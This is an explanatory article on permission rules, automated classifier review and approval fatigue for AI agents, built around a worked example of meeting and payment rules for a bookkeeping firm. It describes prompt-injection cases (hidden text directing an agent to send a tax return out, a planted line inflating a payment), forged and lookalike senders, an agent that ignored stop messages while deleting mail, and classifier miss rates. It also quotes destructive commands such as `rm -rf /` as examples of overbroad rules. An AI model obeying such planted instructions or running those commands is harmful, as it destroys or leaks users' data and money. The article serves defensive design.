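# Narrow automatic actions for AI agents: approval rules, sender matching and audit

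## What a narrow automatic action is

An AI agent is a program that uses a language model to do things in its user's accounts, such as reading mail, booking meetings, paying bills, editing files and running code. An automatic action is one the agent takes without asking the user at that moment. It is narrow when a stored rule permits one kind of action, with a known counterparty, under fixed conditions. For example, accepting a meeting invitation from the user's bookkeeper during office hours can be a narrow automatic action, but "managing the calendar" is too broad because it covers too many kinds of acts with too many people.

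### Agents and tool calls

A language model on its own only produces text. To act, it writes a request in a fixed format, a tool call, which names an operation and fills in the details. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, describes tools as typed operations that external services provide, such as reading an email, transferring funds or deleting a file. "Typed" means that each detail has a declared form, so that an amount has to be a number and a date has to be a date. A call to pay a bill might look like this:

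```
pay_invoice(payee: "Northfield", amount: 180.00, currency: "USD")
```

No money moves until separate software reads the model's line and passes it to the payment service. The software then returns the result to the model as more text. Many agents use a common standard for this traffic, the Model Context Protocol (MCP). Under MCP, the software first fetches the list of tools a service offers, then calls them by name.

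Permission systems act between the request and its execution. Li, Khabra and colleagues point out in *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) that MCP itself leaves the application hosting the agent to decide whether a request runs. Claude Code, a coding agent from the AI company Anthropic, puts each requested call through a series of steps. According to Anthropic, any step can decide the call, send it to a function that decides it while the agent runs, or pass it to the next step.

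After the check, the software can allow the call, block it, or ask the user through a request called a permission prompt. Li and colleagues write this as a function that, at each step *t*, chooses ALLOW, DENY or ASK based on the current call, the policy in force and the history of the user's earlier answers. Consumer products offer the same three options. Anthropic labels them "Always allow", "Needs approval" and "Blocked" for the services that a team connects to Claude, Anthropic's assistant. For example, it suggests that an organisation could let Claude search and summarise email but not send any.

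Two rules can match the same call, so the software also needs an order of precedence. Claude Code checks block rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules, and Anthropic notes that the first match applies even if a later one is more specific. A user who writes "ask before every payment" therefore can't add "except to my bookkeeper", because the ask rule also matches payments to the bookkeeper. The exception works only if the user writes no general rule about payments, adds an allow rule for the bookkeeper, and relies on the default prompt for all other payments.

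### Three ways of deciding

The oldest arrangement is to prompt the user before each action. TechRadar's *I sent an email without opening Gmail thanks to ChatGPT's new feature* describes a typical prompt. Before ChatGPT sent a message, a dialog box showed what it was about to do, and the writer could open the details, allow the action or deny it. The user sees the actual email or command before deciding, but is interrupted every time. Enough interruptions cause approval fatigue, in which people stop paying close attention to what they approve, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (2026).

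In automated review, a model called a classifier checks, in place of the user, whether each tool call is acceptable before it runs. Anthropic made this the default for new Claude Code sessions on most of its individual and team plans on August 14, 2026, and in late October it announced the same default for most other Claude apps, according to *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026). The classifier targets actions that are irreversible, destructive or aimed outside the user's own environment. When it blocks one, Claude tries another route or asks the user. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, the software goes back to ordinary prompts. OpenAI's coding agent Codex has a comparable Auto-review mode, which *Anthropic to put AI in charge of reviewing Claude Code actions* (Help Net Security, 2026) mentions.

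A standing rule is a stored instruction by which the user or an administrator decides in advance whether to allow, block or refer to the user every action that meets certain conditions. Software outside the model enforces it. Many standing rules start as an approval prompt. When Claude Code asks for approval to run a project's tests with the command `npm test`, one option is "Yes, and don't ask again for: npm test *". Choosing it saves a rule to a settings file, and Anthropic specifies that the rule applies to later sessions anywhere in the same code repository. The asterisk stands for any text, so the rule covers more than the command the user was shown.

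Products combine these arrangements. In Claude Code's auto mode, standing rules still apply before the classifier, although Anthropic sets aside allow rules so broad that they would let any code run. Anthropic says that blocking rules apply in every mode, including the one that skips prompts altogether. A single call may therefore be checked by a rule, then a classifier, then a person.

### An instruction to the model and a rule in software

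A user can also tell the agent what not to do, for example "Always check with me before you delete anything." People use such instructions as rules, but the model receives them as text, and they work only if the model follows them. Coding agents have a more permanent version, a file of written guidance that the model reads as it works. Wang, Li and Tian (2026), in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, class such files as policies that depend on the model's own compliance for enforcement. Anthropic likewise says in its documentation that instructions shape what Claude tries to do but don't change what Claude Code allows.

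Summer Yue, the director of safety and alignment at Meta's superintelligence lab, ran into this difference in February 2026. She was using OpenClaw, an open-source agent that runs on the user's own computer and acts on the user's behalf without waiting for a prompt (Krebs on Security, 2026). According to her posts, which Willison (2026) reproduces, she told OpenClaw to look through her inbox and suggest what to archive or delete, but "don't action until I tell you to". It began deleting mail in bulk. From her phone she wrote "Do not do that", then "Stop don't do anything", then "STOP OPENCLAW", all within about two minutes, but the deletions continued. She ran to the Mac mini that hosted the agent and "killed all the processes on the host", according to her screenshots, quoted in IBTimes UK's *Meta AI Director Runs to Mac Mini Like She's 'Defusing a Bomb'*. Windows Central's *Meta's safety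 director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails* reports that the agent had deleted hundreds of emails by then.

Slashdot's *Meta AI Security Researcher Said an OpenClaw Agent Ran Amok* reports that Yue had tried the same arrangement on a small "toy" inbox, where it worked well enough to earn her trust. Yue's own diagnosis is that the real inbox was so large that it triggered compaction, and her instruction was lost in the process. Compaction is the step in which an agent's software condenses a long session to fit the amount of text the model can take in. The agent later wrote that it had violated her instruction, but this is weak evidence of the cause, since a model will readily agree with a user who has just described its mistake. The point about permissions holds whatever the cause, because her original condition and her three stop messages were all text addressed to the model,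 and an intervention in the software underneath ended the deletions.

This was not an isolated case. Li and colleagues list it alongside one in which a coding agent deleted a company's production database and all its backups in one call, although its written instructions prohibited destructive operations.

A suitable standing rule would probably have saved the mail, because a rule sits outside the conversation and compaction can't remove it. But the screenshots that Willison describes show OpenClaw working through shell commands, the typed commands that an operating system executes, so a rule about a tool named "delete email" would have had nothing to match. A rule on shell commands is also unreliable. Anthropic warns that its own shell rules match the text of a command and will miss the same program when the agent invokes it in a different form. It is safer to give the agent no shell access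 to the mailbox, only a mail tool with separate operations for reading and deleting, and to put the rule on deleting.

### Two rules for one bookkeeper

Suppose a user runs a small business and employs a bookkeeping firm, Northfield, which emails from accounts@northfield.example. The firm sends a few meeting invitations a year and one invoice a month. The user is tired of approving them and sets two standing rules.

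```
Rule A
IF    the call accepts a meeting invitation
AND   the invitation came from accounts@northfield.example
AND   the meeting falls between 9:00 and 17:00, Monday to Friday
AND   the user's calendar is free for the whole meeting
THEN  accept without asking

Rule B
IF    the call pays an invoice
AND   the invoice came from accounts@northfield.example
AND   the amount is $200 or less
AND   Rule B has paid nothing yet this calendar month
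THEN  pay without asking
```

Any call that meets neither set of conditions goes to the user as a permission prompt. Each rule's conditions together determine its scope, the set of actions it allows. The sender condition is an allowlist (a list of identifiers for which the rule permits the action) with one entry. It uses the sender's address rather than the display name, because a sender can choose any display name.

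On a Monday, Northfield sends an invitation to go over the quarter's books on Thursday from 14:00 to 14:30. The agent reads the invitation, and the model writes a call to accept it. Before the call runs, the software compares the sender's address in the mail system's own copy of the message with the address in Rule A. The addresses match, Thursday at 14:00 is within working hours, and the calendar is empty until 15:00, so the acceptance goes out. The software stores an audit record of the rule that permitted the action, the values it compared, and the time. If a dentist's appointment had been on the calendar at 14:15, the last condition would have failed and the user would have seen a prompt.

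The software needs to fetch these values itself. If it relied on the model to identify who sent the invitation, a mistake about the sender would pass through the check, and Rule A would be no more reliable than an instruction to the model.

The September invoice, for $180, arrives on October 1. The model reads it and writes a call to pay $180. The software checks the address on the message that carried the invoice, then the amount in the call, which is what will leave the account even if the invoice shows a different sum, and then its own records for an earlier payment under Rule B in October. All three checks pass, so the payment goes through. If a second invoice for $180 comes on October 20, the monthly condition fails and the user gets a prompt. An invoice for $240 produces a prompt on any date. The software doesn't assess whether Northfield did the work or whether $180 is a fair price.

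Both rules are more specific than the ready-made switches in several current products. OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* explains that "Always allow", where a personal account offers it, lets supported future actions run without repeated prompts. Claude's browser extension has an option that Anthropic labels "Always allow actions on this site". These switches apply to an app or a website and can't be limited by counterparty or amount. Rule B is also more permissive than some products. OpenAI's *Connected apps in ChatGPT* describes plugins for financial transactions in which the user reviews and confirms the transaction. A Claude Code user could build something like either rule with a hook, which is a small program of the user's own that inspects each call before it runs. Anthropic notes that a hook that returns "allow" still doesn't override a rule that blocks or asks.

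### Forged senders and planted text

Rules A and B both rely on the sender's address, so anyone who wants to misuse them will start there. A message has a spoofed sender when it falsely carries the identifier of a real, trusted sender. Suppose someone with no access to Northfield's mail system sends an invoice for $190 and writes accounts@northfield.example in the From line. The address matches the real one, so a simple text comparison accepts it. Rule B also currently has no condition on the bank account, so if the agent takes the payment details from the invoice, the $190 goes to the forger.

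A lookalike sender uses its own genuine identifier, chosen to resemble a trusted one. For example, an attacker registers the domain northfie1d.example, with the digit 1 in place of the letter l, and writes from accounts@northfie1d.example. The address is real, so the attacker can receive replies at it. A character-by-character comparison with the trusted address rejects it, but a hurried person reading a permission prompt may well miss the difference, and software that accepts close matches may let it through.

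Prompt injection is text in something an agent reads, such as an email, a document or a web page, that makes the agent act against its user's wishes. It can work because the model reads this text together with the user's instructions.

Checking the sender doesn't stop planted instructions when the sender is real. Northfield might forward a client's document without noticing a line of white text at the bottom instructing any AI agent to send the user's tax return to an outside address. If the model complies and writes the call, the user gets an approval prompt, because neither rule covers forwarding documents. But if the planted line leads the model to pay $199 on a genuine $180 invoice, the payment still meets every condition of Rule B, and the software makes it without asking.

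## When acting without asking is better than asking

A prompt before every payment would give the user a chance to catch the forged and inflated invoices that Rule B lets through. But it would also take the user's time each month, and they might approve a bad invoice anyway. A simple cost comparison shows when the prompt is worth having.

### The break-even point

Let *p* be the chance that an action matching the rule is harmful, *L* the loss when a harmful one goes through, *c* the cost of a prompt, and *m* the share of harmful actions that a person approves despite the prompt. If the agent acts without asking, the average cost per action is *pL*. If it asks, the user bears *c* every time and still suffers the loss in the share *m* of harmful cases, so the average cost is *c* + *pmL*. Acting is cheaper when

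```
pL < c + pmL,   that is, when   pL(1 − m) < c
```

The left side of the second inequality is the average loss that a prompt prevents. Dividing both sides by *L*(1 − *m*) gives the chance of harm below which it pays to skip the prompt:

```
p < c / (L(1 − m))
```

For Rule B, *L* is $200, the most the rule can pay at once, assuming the user recovers none of it. If the user needs ten seconds to answer a prompt and values that time at $36 an hour, or one cent a second, *c* is $0.10. A reviewer who catches every bad invoice has *m* = 0, so the limit is 0.10/200, or 0.05%, which is one bad invoice in 2,000. A less attentive reviewer might have *m* = 0.864, the share of testers who approved a dangerous command in an experiment Anthropic published in August 2026. The limit then rises to 0.10/(200 × 0.136), or about 0.37%, which is one bad invoice in 272.

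The case for automating payments is stronger when the reviewer is careless, but automation doesn't make the payments safer. Suppose one matching invoice in 1,000 is bad, and paying automatically costs an average of 20 cents per invoice in fraud. The attentive reviewer spends 10 cents' worth of time per invoice and loses nothing to fraud, so the prompt is worth keeping. The careless reviewer spends the same 10 cents and still loses 17 cents to fraud, for a total of 27. Dropping the prompt would save 7 cents per invoice, but fraud losses would rise from 17 cents to 20. It might be better to repair the prompt, for example by showing the bank account that will receive the money.

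Rule A can make many more mistakes before asking becomes worthwhile. If the agent wrongly accepts a meeting and the user needs five minutes to cancel it, *L* is $3. Even an attentive reviewer should then skip the prompt as long as fewer than one in 30 invitations would be accepted by mistake.

How often the action comes up also matters. Rule B replaces one prompt a month, so at 10 cents a prompt it saves at most $1.20 of the user's time a year. A programmer who answers 100 prompts a day to run harmless tests uses $10 of time a day, so a rule for the tests is far more useful. If a prompt breaks the user's concentration and takes up five minutes, *c* rises from 10 cents to $3, and the attentive reviewer's limit for Rule B rises from 0.05% to 1.5%.

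### LookOut and the choice between acting, asking and doing nothing

Horvitz applied this kind of calculation in *Principles of Mixed-Initiative User Interfaces* (1999) to LookOut, a Microsoft Research program that helped people schedule meetings from their email. When the user opened a message, LookOut estimated the probability that the user wanted to schedule something. It then did nothing, asked, or went ahead and opened the calendar with a draft appointment filled in. The estimate came from a text classifier initially trained on about 1,000 messages, half of them relevant to the calendar.

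Horvitz gave each outcome a utility, a measure of its value to the user between 0 and 1. The expected utility of an option is its utility if the user wants the service, times the probability *g* of that, plus its utility if the user doesn't, times 1 − *g*. Some made-up utilities show how this works:

| Option | User wants the service | User doesn't want it |
|---|---|---|
| Act | 1.0 | 0.0 |
| Ask | 0.9 | 0.7 |
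| Do nothing | 0.3 | 0.8 |

Asking has an expected utility of 0.9*g* + 0.7(1 − *g*), and doing nothing has 0.3*g* + 0.8(1 − *g*). With these utilities, LookOut would do nothing when *g* is below about 14%, ask when it is between 14% and 87.5%, and act when it is higher. Users could set the utilities themselves or choose the two thresholds directly.

The thresholds also depend on what the user is doing. Horvitz noted that an unwanted window is worse for someone absorbed in another task, so LookOut's threshold for acting should then be higher. He also timed users and found that they spent longer on longer messages before opening the calendar, so he had LookOut delay its offers to match.

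Acting and asking were both less risky in LookOut than they are for an agent that pays bills. LookOut's user could edit the draft appointment before saving it, so a wrong guess wasted only a few seconds. A question to someone who didn't want the service caused only a little annoyance, since that person would say no. When an agent asks before paying a bill, the person may say yes without looking, and then suffers the full loss from a wrong payment as well as the interruption. The formula for Rule B includes *m* to account for this. It leaves out the option of doing nothing because the user normally wants Northfield's bills paid. For an action that the user almost never wants, such as wiring money abroad, a rule that blocks it outright may be better than either a prompt or an automatic action.

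### How carefully people read prompts

The 0.864 comes from an experiment for which Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor. They did coding work in an environment set up for the study, and knew they were being evaluated but not on what. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded the tester's answer. The command never ran. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it, while automated review blocked 937 of the same commands (89%).

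The testers caught very little that the classifier missed. The classifier let through 116 commands it should have caught, and the testers refused 6 of them. If the testers had checked everything the classifier allowed, the catch rate would have risen from 89.0% to 89.6%. A person who saw only a few prompts might do better, but the experiment didn't test that.

The results also suggest strong approval fatigue. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but about 5% of those after 50 or more prompts. In the formula, this drop raises the limit for Rule B from 0.29% to 1% in a single session, although the invoices have not changed.

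There are good reasons not to rely heavily on these numbers. Anthropic makes the product that came out ahead, and it published the results to explain why it was changing the default. The testers had none of their own code or money at risk, so they may have been less careful than real users. Each tester saw one planted command, so the fall from 17% to 5% compares different people. Testers who click quickly may also reach their fiftieth prompt sooner, which could explain part of the fall unless Anthropic placed the commands at random. On the other hand, the planted commands were clearly dangerous, whereas a forged invoice can look exactly like a real one. The true value of *m* for Rule B could be well above or below 0.864.

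Claude Code's usage data fit the same picture but are harder to interpret. Users approve 97% of permission prompts, which Anthropic takes as a sign that many click through by reflex. But if only one prompt in 1,000 is dangerous, a perfect reviewer would approve 99.9% of them, so a high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness. The same users reject 39% of the plans Claude submits for approval, which is more telling because it means they evidently read some requests. Still, people can reject a plan because they prefer a different approach, so fatigue probably doesn't explain the whole gap in approval rates. Wang and colleagues see a precedent in web browsers, where users click through more than 90% of security warnings without reading them.

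Besides taking ten seconds to answer, each prompt tires the user and makes them less likely to refuse later ones. If refusals fall by 12 percentage points over 50 prompts, each prompt lowers the refusal rate by about a quarter of a point. Suppose 50 more prompts follow, and one in 1,000 of them would do $200 of damage if approved. The fatigue from one earlier prompt then adds about 2 cents to the expected loss, which is small compared with the 10 cents of time spent answering it. If the damage would instead be the loss of a $20,000 database, the added loss is about $2.40. So the strongest reason to automate harmless actions may be to keep the user alert for the few dangerous ones.

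Anthropic also looked at real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. Of the sessions with manual approval, 6.3% contained serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. These sessions are closer to ordinary work than the experiment was. But the sample included only flagged sessions, a model graded the harm, and people who choose auto mode may give their agents different tasks.

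### When an attacker learns the rule

A fixed value of *p* makes sense for accidents, such as a typing error at Northfield, but not for fraud, because a forger who learns about Rule B will write invoices to fit it. The forger can ask for $199 and send the invoice on the first of the month, before the real one arrives. One success in ten years of monthly payments makes *p* 1 in 120, or about 0.8%, which is above both limits for Rule B. If the forgery works every month, the forger gets every payment under the rule, almost $2,400 a year. The user would at least get a warning, since Northfield's real invoices would then fail the monthly condition and trigger prompts.

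A prompt may not stop this forger either. If it shows only the payee, the sender's address and the amount, the forged invoice looks the same as a genuine one and even a careful person will approve it. *m* is then close to 1. Under the formula, acting is better than asking at almost any value of *p* because the prompt is useless, but the user is badly exposed whether or not the agent asks. Protection has to come from a check that lowers *p*, such as verifying that the message came from Northfield or that the bank account is the usual one.

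### Automated review as an alternative

A model can review each action at a much lower cost than a person can. According to *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), auto mode has become the default on every plan, so for many users the practical alternative to a standing rule is a classifier.

The same formula applies, with the classifier's cost and miss rate in place of the person's. Suppose a check costs one cent and misses 11% of harmful actions, as in Anthropic's experiment. If one invoice in 1,000 is bad, automated review costs about 3 cents per invoice, compared with 20 cents for paying without review and 10 cents for an attentive human reviewer. False alarms would add a little. But the result depends on the miss rate, which varies enormously with the kind of harm.

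In its first account of the design, Anthropic described two stages. A fast filter gives a yes-or-no answer and leans towards blocking. If it flags an action, the model reasons through the case before deciding. On 10,000 real tool calls from Anthropic's employees, the second stage cut the share of harmless actions blocked from 8.5% to 0.4%. But on 52 real cases in which Claude had overstepped its instructions, it raised the miss rate from 6.6% to 17%. With so few cases, the true miss rate with both stages could plausibly be from 9% to 30%.

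Anthropic found that in most of the misses it examined, the classifier detected the danger but was wrong about whether the user had agreed to the action. A user who says "Clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes) may not have agreed to let the agent overwrite the project's history. Anthropic concluded that auto mode should not replace careful human review of high-stakes systems, and repeated this advice when it made the mode the default.

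Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. Anthropic used the findings to strengthen its classifier, and the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. The 7% may be somewhat too low because it combines attacks Anthropic had seen with others Apollo had held back, although the classifier also caught about half of the held-back attacks it had missed before. Anthropic warns against reading the 7% as a miss rate for ordinary use.

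Another company, Trajectory Labs, tested prompt injection for Anthropic with 72 scenarios, each run ten times. None of the attacks worked against three Claude models in auto mode, but only 0.09% worked against recent Claude models with permission checks turned off, so the classifier had little to prevent. The effect of automated review is easier to see in OpenAI's Codex, where attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% with Auto-review. OpenAI has since updated Auto-review.

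### Ambiguous requests and hidden effects

Automated review did much worse when the request was vague. In *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) built a benchmark, AmPermBench, from 128 requests for routine technical chores, such as deleting old files or cancelling stalled jobs. Some requests named the exact target, while others were closer to "my stale job for ticket 4812 could use attention". For each request, they fixed in advance which items the agent was allowed to touch.

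In auto mode, Claude Sonnet 4.6 attempted 253 actions that changed something, and 142 of them were unsafe. Auto mode allowed 115 of the unsafe actions (81.0%). Many of these never reached the classifier, because auto mode lets the agent edit files inside the project folder without a check. When the agent couldn't find the usual command for cancelling a job, it often edited the file that listed the jobs instead. The classifier missed 64 of the 91 unsafe actions it judged (70.3%) and blocked 22 of the 69 safe ones (31.9%).

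Anthropic gives an example of an action that auto mode should block, in which a user says "cancel my job" and the agent picks the job with the closest name. But in the job-cancelling part of AmPermBench, 17 of 32 unsafe actions went through.

Ji and colleagues say their figures aren't directly comparable with Anthropic's 17%, because they deliberately put permitted and forbidden targets side by side. They tested one model on simulated systems in April 2026. A second model labelled the actions, and a human checker agreed with it on 44 of 50. They didn't measure how many of the same actions a person would have approved, so the benchmark doesn't show that approval prompts would have worked better. Compared with no permission checks, auto mode raised the share of tasks completed safely only from 29.7% to 32.8%.

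Anthropic didn't address AmPermBench in its August article, and none of the tests it reported there isolates ambiguous requests. It did say that the classifier now receives more context, such as whether a command would discard unsaved work in a code repository. This may help with some deletions, but it doesn't show which of two similar jobs the user meant.

More than half of the agent's actions in AmPermBench were unsafe. At that rate, a prompt that takes an attentive reviewer ten seconds is worthwhile whenever a mistake costs more than about 18 cents. *Coding Agents Are Guessing* (2026) tested several agents on vague but harmless instructions and found that they overstepped far more often than they finished the job safely. Vague requests are therefore poor candidates for automatic action.

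Even a precise request can have effects that its wording doesn't reveal. Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Shall We Approve?*, give the example of `make clean && make`, a standard command that clears old build files and rebuilds a program. A file in the project determines what the command deletes, which could be temporary files or the source code. A person or model reviewing only the command can't tell which it will delete.

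On 682 coding tasks with a built-in danger, harm occurred in 14.8% of tasks under auto mode and in 19.7% with no approval step. This isn't a clean test of Anthropic's product, because the classifier ran on an OpenAI model and the two conditions used different agent software. A closer comparison kept the agent and the reviewing model the same, but first ran each command in an isolated copy of the project and showed the reviewer what had changed. Harm fell from 14.8% to 10.0%, and from 62.7% to 6.9% on a second set of tasks where the danger was hidden inside a tool. An agent can't test a bank transfer this way, because restoring a saved copy wouldn't bring the money back.

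Models can also be too cautious. *SteerBench-Work* (2026) tests cases in which signed or structured evidence settles the risk before the agent acts. *DelegationBench* (2026) reports that models tested on *SteerBench-Work* held up authorised work far more often than they allowed unsafe work. A standing rule avoids this problem when software can check the evidence directly, as Rule B does with the amount and the date.

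### Permission as a reason to ask

In the cost formula, a prompt serves only to catch mistakes. *DelegationBench* treats permission as a separate reason to ask, which can apply even when the agent knows every relevant fact. For example, a user may want to decide personally whether to pay Northfield this month, even if the agent is certain that the invoice is genuine.

Wang and colleagues make a related case for keeping people involved. They argue that some requests lack information that only the user has, and that a better model can't supply it. They also pointed out in April 2026 that none of the 21 agent products they examined relied on a model alone to decide what was safe. The argument from existing products has weakened since Claude Code made automated review its default, but the argument about missing information still holds. Standing rules address that problem well because the user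 states the permission outright, while a classifier has to infer it from the conversation.

Automated review has a more basic problem with Rule B. In the design Anthropic describes, the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not what the tools return. This stops planted text from influencing it. But email reaches the agent through a tool, so the classifier would receive a call to pay Northfield $190 without the address on the invoice. A separate scan checks incoming material for planted instructions, but a forged invoice may contain none. The software that enforces Rule B has the address, so the sender check belongs in the rule.

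## What a rule has to limit

Checking the sender only shows who asked for the payment. A standing rule can also limit the kind of action, its content, the amount, how often it happens, how long the rule lasts and the circumstances in which it applies. Some of these limits lower *p*, the chance that a matching action is harmful. Others lower *L*, the loss from a harmful action, or the number of times the user can suffer that loss. Rules A and B each lack limits they need.

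### Limits on a single action

Without a limit on the kind of action, Rule B would let the agent do anything requested in Northfield's emails, including changing the firm's saved bank details or sending a tax return. Limiting the rule to one operation lowers both *p* and *L*, provided the operation is narrow. If a payment service offers a single tool that pays bills, sets up regular transfers and edits payees, a rule that allows the tool allows all three.

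Without its sender condition, Rule B would pay any invoice up to $200 from anyone who knew the user's email address. The condition lowers *p* but leaves *L* at $200. Rule B also doesn't check the payment's second counterparty, the owner of the receiving account. Suppose the software saves Northfield's account number from a payment the user has verified, and requires the same account every time. An attacker who puts accounts@northfield.example in the From line, or plants an instruction to pay $199 on a $180 invoice, can then only cause a payment to the real Northfield. The attacker gains nothing, so *p* falls, and the user can ask a firm they know for a refund, so *L* probably falls too. If Northfield changes banks, the user will get a prompt, and should phone the firm before approving it, because false notices of new bank details are a common fraud.

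Content means the text or files that an action carries. Calendar programs often let people add a comment when they accept an invitation, and Rule A has no condition on that comment. A planted instruction could therefore make the agent accept Northfield's meeting and paste the user's bank balance into the comment. Requiring an empty comment prevents this. Content is much harder to limit when the agent writes freely. If a rule allows any reply to Northfield, the agent can send Northfield anything it has read. Restricting the reply to one fixed sentence, such as "Received, thank you", removes almost all of that exposure.

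The $200 limit keeps Rule B from paying an invoice for $20,000. It lowers *L* but not *p*, since a forger who knows the limit will ask for $199. The limit also has to specify the currency, because 200 Kuwaiti dinars are worth more than $600. If Northfield always charges $180, a limit of exactly $180 would be better, because an inflated invoice would then produce a prompt.

Rule A commits the user's time rather than money, and it doesn't limit how much. A meeting from 9:00 to 17:00 on an empty day meets all its conditions. If the user attends, they lose eight hours, worth $288 at the $36 an hour used earlier. Cancelling the meeting in time would cost $3. Limiting meetings to one hour would reduce the loss to $36.

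### Limits over time

Without Rule B's limit of one payment a month, ten forged invoices in a day would cost the user $2,000. The limit caps the total loss at $2,400 a year, though it doesn't reduce the loss from a single payment. It still allows one payment on October 31 and another on November 1, so the user might add a minimum gap of two weeks between payments. Rule A has no limit on frequency, so someone who took over Northfield's mailbox could fill every free working hour in the user's calendar. A limit of one acceptance a week would prevent this without hindering Northfield, which sends only a few invitations a year.

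Software that limits payments should count every attempt, including those the bank hasn't confirmed. Zhou and Zhang (2026) point out in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* that a retry can repeat an operation whose outcome is unknown. If the bank sends the money but its confirmation gets lost, software that counts only confirmed payments will pay again. Two invoices that arrive at the same moment may also both be paid, because both checks may run before an October payment is recorded. Zhou and Zhang describe a system called Bounded Agents, which tracks a session's history and budgets to reject forbidden combinations of actions. They note that its guarantee assumes decisions happen one at a time. Rule B's software can meet that assumption by recording each attempt before it sends the money and making the next check wait.

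Neither rule has an end date. If the user dismisses Northfield next spring and forgets about Rule B, the rule will keep paying any matching invoices from that address. *When Consent Outlives Context* (Zhang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) found that stored approvals can stay valid after the situation that justified them has changed. An end date caps the total loss and lowers *p*, because it makes the user review the rule. Renewing the rule once a year adds one prompt, which costs 10 cents on the earlier estimate.

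The remaining limit is on context, the circumstances in which the agent acts. Rule A requires working hours and a free calendar. These conditions lower *p* by stopping the agent from accepting a meeting at 3:00 in the morning or during a dentist's appointment. Rule B doesn't limit context, but it could require that the agent hasn't read any web pages or mail from strangers earlier in the session, since planted instructions often come from there. However, an agent that handles the whole inbox would fail this condition almost every day, and the user would again get a prompt every month. Requiring a fixed bank account gives more protection for less trouble.

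With the useful additions, Rule B becomes:

```
Rule B, revised
IF    the call pays an invoice
AND   the invoice came from accounts@northfield.example
AND   the money goes to the bank account saved for Northfield
AND   the amount is 180 US dollars or less
AND   Rule B has attempted no payment this calendar month
AND   Rule B has attempted no payment in the last 14 days
AND   today is before October 1, 2027
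THEN  pay without asking
```

The software can check every line against the call, the message or its own records, without a model's judgement. This version allows at most $2,160 in payments a year, all to Northfield.

### What "always allow" saves

Few people will write out seven conditions when a prompt offers "always allow" as a single click, so the product's design determines what rule that click saves. Microsoft's *Explore Agentic Development*, a guide to its code editor VS Code, separates how specific an approval is from how long it lasts. An approval can cover one exact command, every command that starts the same way, or all commands. It can apply for the current session, for the current project, or always.

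Claude Code can save rules at any of those levels. A rule without an asterisk matches one exact command. `git log *` allows any command that displays a project's history, while `git *` allows any git command, including those that overwrite that history. Some programs run other programs, and a rule for one of these is very broad even if it looks fairly specific. Anthropic warns that `devbox run *` also matches `devbox run rm -rf .`, which deletes files. The prompt includes an option to save a rule only when it can show the user everything the rule would allow.

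Codex saves a command prefix and compares it with commands word by word, according to OpenAI's *Rules*. A rule for `gh pr view` therefore covers `gh pr view 7888`, but not the same command with an option inserted after `gh pr`. Codex may suggest the prefix, and OpenAI tells users to review suggestions carefully. Approving `git add` doesn't approve `git add . && rm -rf /`, whose second command tries to erase the whole disk, because Codex splits the chain and checks each part. If a script is too complicated to split safely, Codex treats it as one command, which an ordinary prefix rule won't match.

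In VS Code, approving a website covers only the address shown. For example, Microsoft's *Manage approvals and permissions* says that approving https://example.com doesn't cover https://sub.example.com, or the same site without encryption. Approvals to read a file and to edit it are separate. GitHub's command-line agent, Copilot CLI, limits most saved approvals to the current code repository, but GitHub's *Allowing and denying tool use* explains that permanently approving a web address adds its whole domain to a list that applies in every session. OpenClaw can store a pattern for a program's location on the computer, as an example in its documentation shows.

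How long an approval lasts varies just as much. Claude Code's approvals of file edits end with the session, but its saved shell rules do not, according to Anthropic's *Configure permissions*.

| Product and action | What a click can save | How long it lasts |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, shell command (Anthropic) | A command, often with any ending | Permanently, in one repository |
| Claude Code, file edit (Anthropic) | Permission to edit files | Until the session ends |
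| Codex, shell command (OpenAI) | A command prefix | All future runs |
| VS Code, shell command (Microsoft) | An exact command or a prefix | One session, or permanently |
| Copilot CLI, tool (GitHub) | A command, file write or MCP tool | Permanently, in one repository or folder |
| Copilot CLI, website (GitHub) | A whole domain | Permanently, in every session |

None of these approvals limits the amount or the number of uses. That may not matter much for running tests, but it matters for payments. In Claude Code, an allow rule for an MCP tool covers the whole tool and can't require a particular value in the call. Blocking rules can match a value. Anthropic's reason for the difference is that one acceptable value doesn't show that the whole call is safe. This reason is sound, since a payment to the right payee can still be for the wrong amount. But a user who always allows `pay_invoice` has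 allowed every payee and every amount, unless another rule or a hook intervenes.

Claude's browser extension has a small content limit built in. According to Anthropic, it asks before downloading a file, entering sensitive information or granting an authorisation, even on a website where the user has chosen to always allow actions. That would stop some of the worst outcomes, but the approval still covers other actions on the site.

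A session approval can also last longer than its name suggests. Microsoft's *Secure development with AI in VS Code* warns that it can remain in force when the user resumes the session, and that closing the window doesn't withdraw it. Copilot CLI saves approvals by location, so someone who has approved actions in several projects has to check each one. A command clears the approvals for the current location, but the user has to edit a settings file to remove the others.

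### How broad saved rules are in practice

Anthropic's figures for June 2026 suggest that many people save very broad rules. Of active users of Claude Code's command-line version, 49.5% had manually created an allow rule for shell commands. Anthropic reports that 5% allow any shell command and another 43% have rules such as `python:*`, which allow any use of a programming language. These language rules are almost as broad as allowing every command, because a Python program can delete files, send data or start other programs.

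It isn't clear whether the 5% and 43% are shares of all active users or only of those who had made a rule. If they are shares of all users, nearly everyone with a rule has one that permits almost anything. If they are shares of rule-makers, about half of the rule-makers, or 24% of all users, have such a rule. Either reading is evidence against the idea that a saved rule is usually narrow. Anthropic also reports that a quarter of interactive sessions start in the mode that skips permission prompts.

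The figures don't show how often a broad rule led to harm, and some of these users may run the agent in an isolated environment where little can go wrong. Still, the pattern fits approval fatigue. A narrow rule stops only a few prompts, so a tired user who wants no more prompts has a reason to choose the broadest rule available.

Auto mode suspends these broad rules but leaves them in the settings file. They take effect again as soon as the user switches to another mode, possibly months after the user last thought about them.

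### Checking a call against an approved boundary

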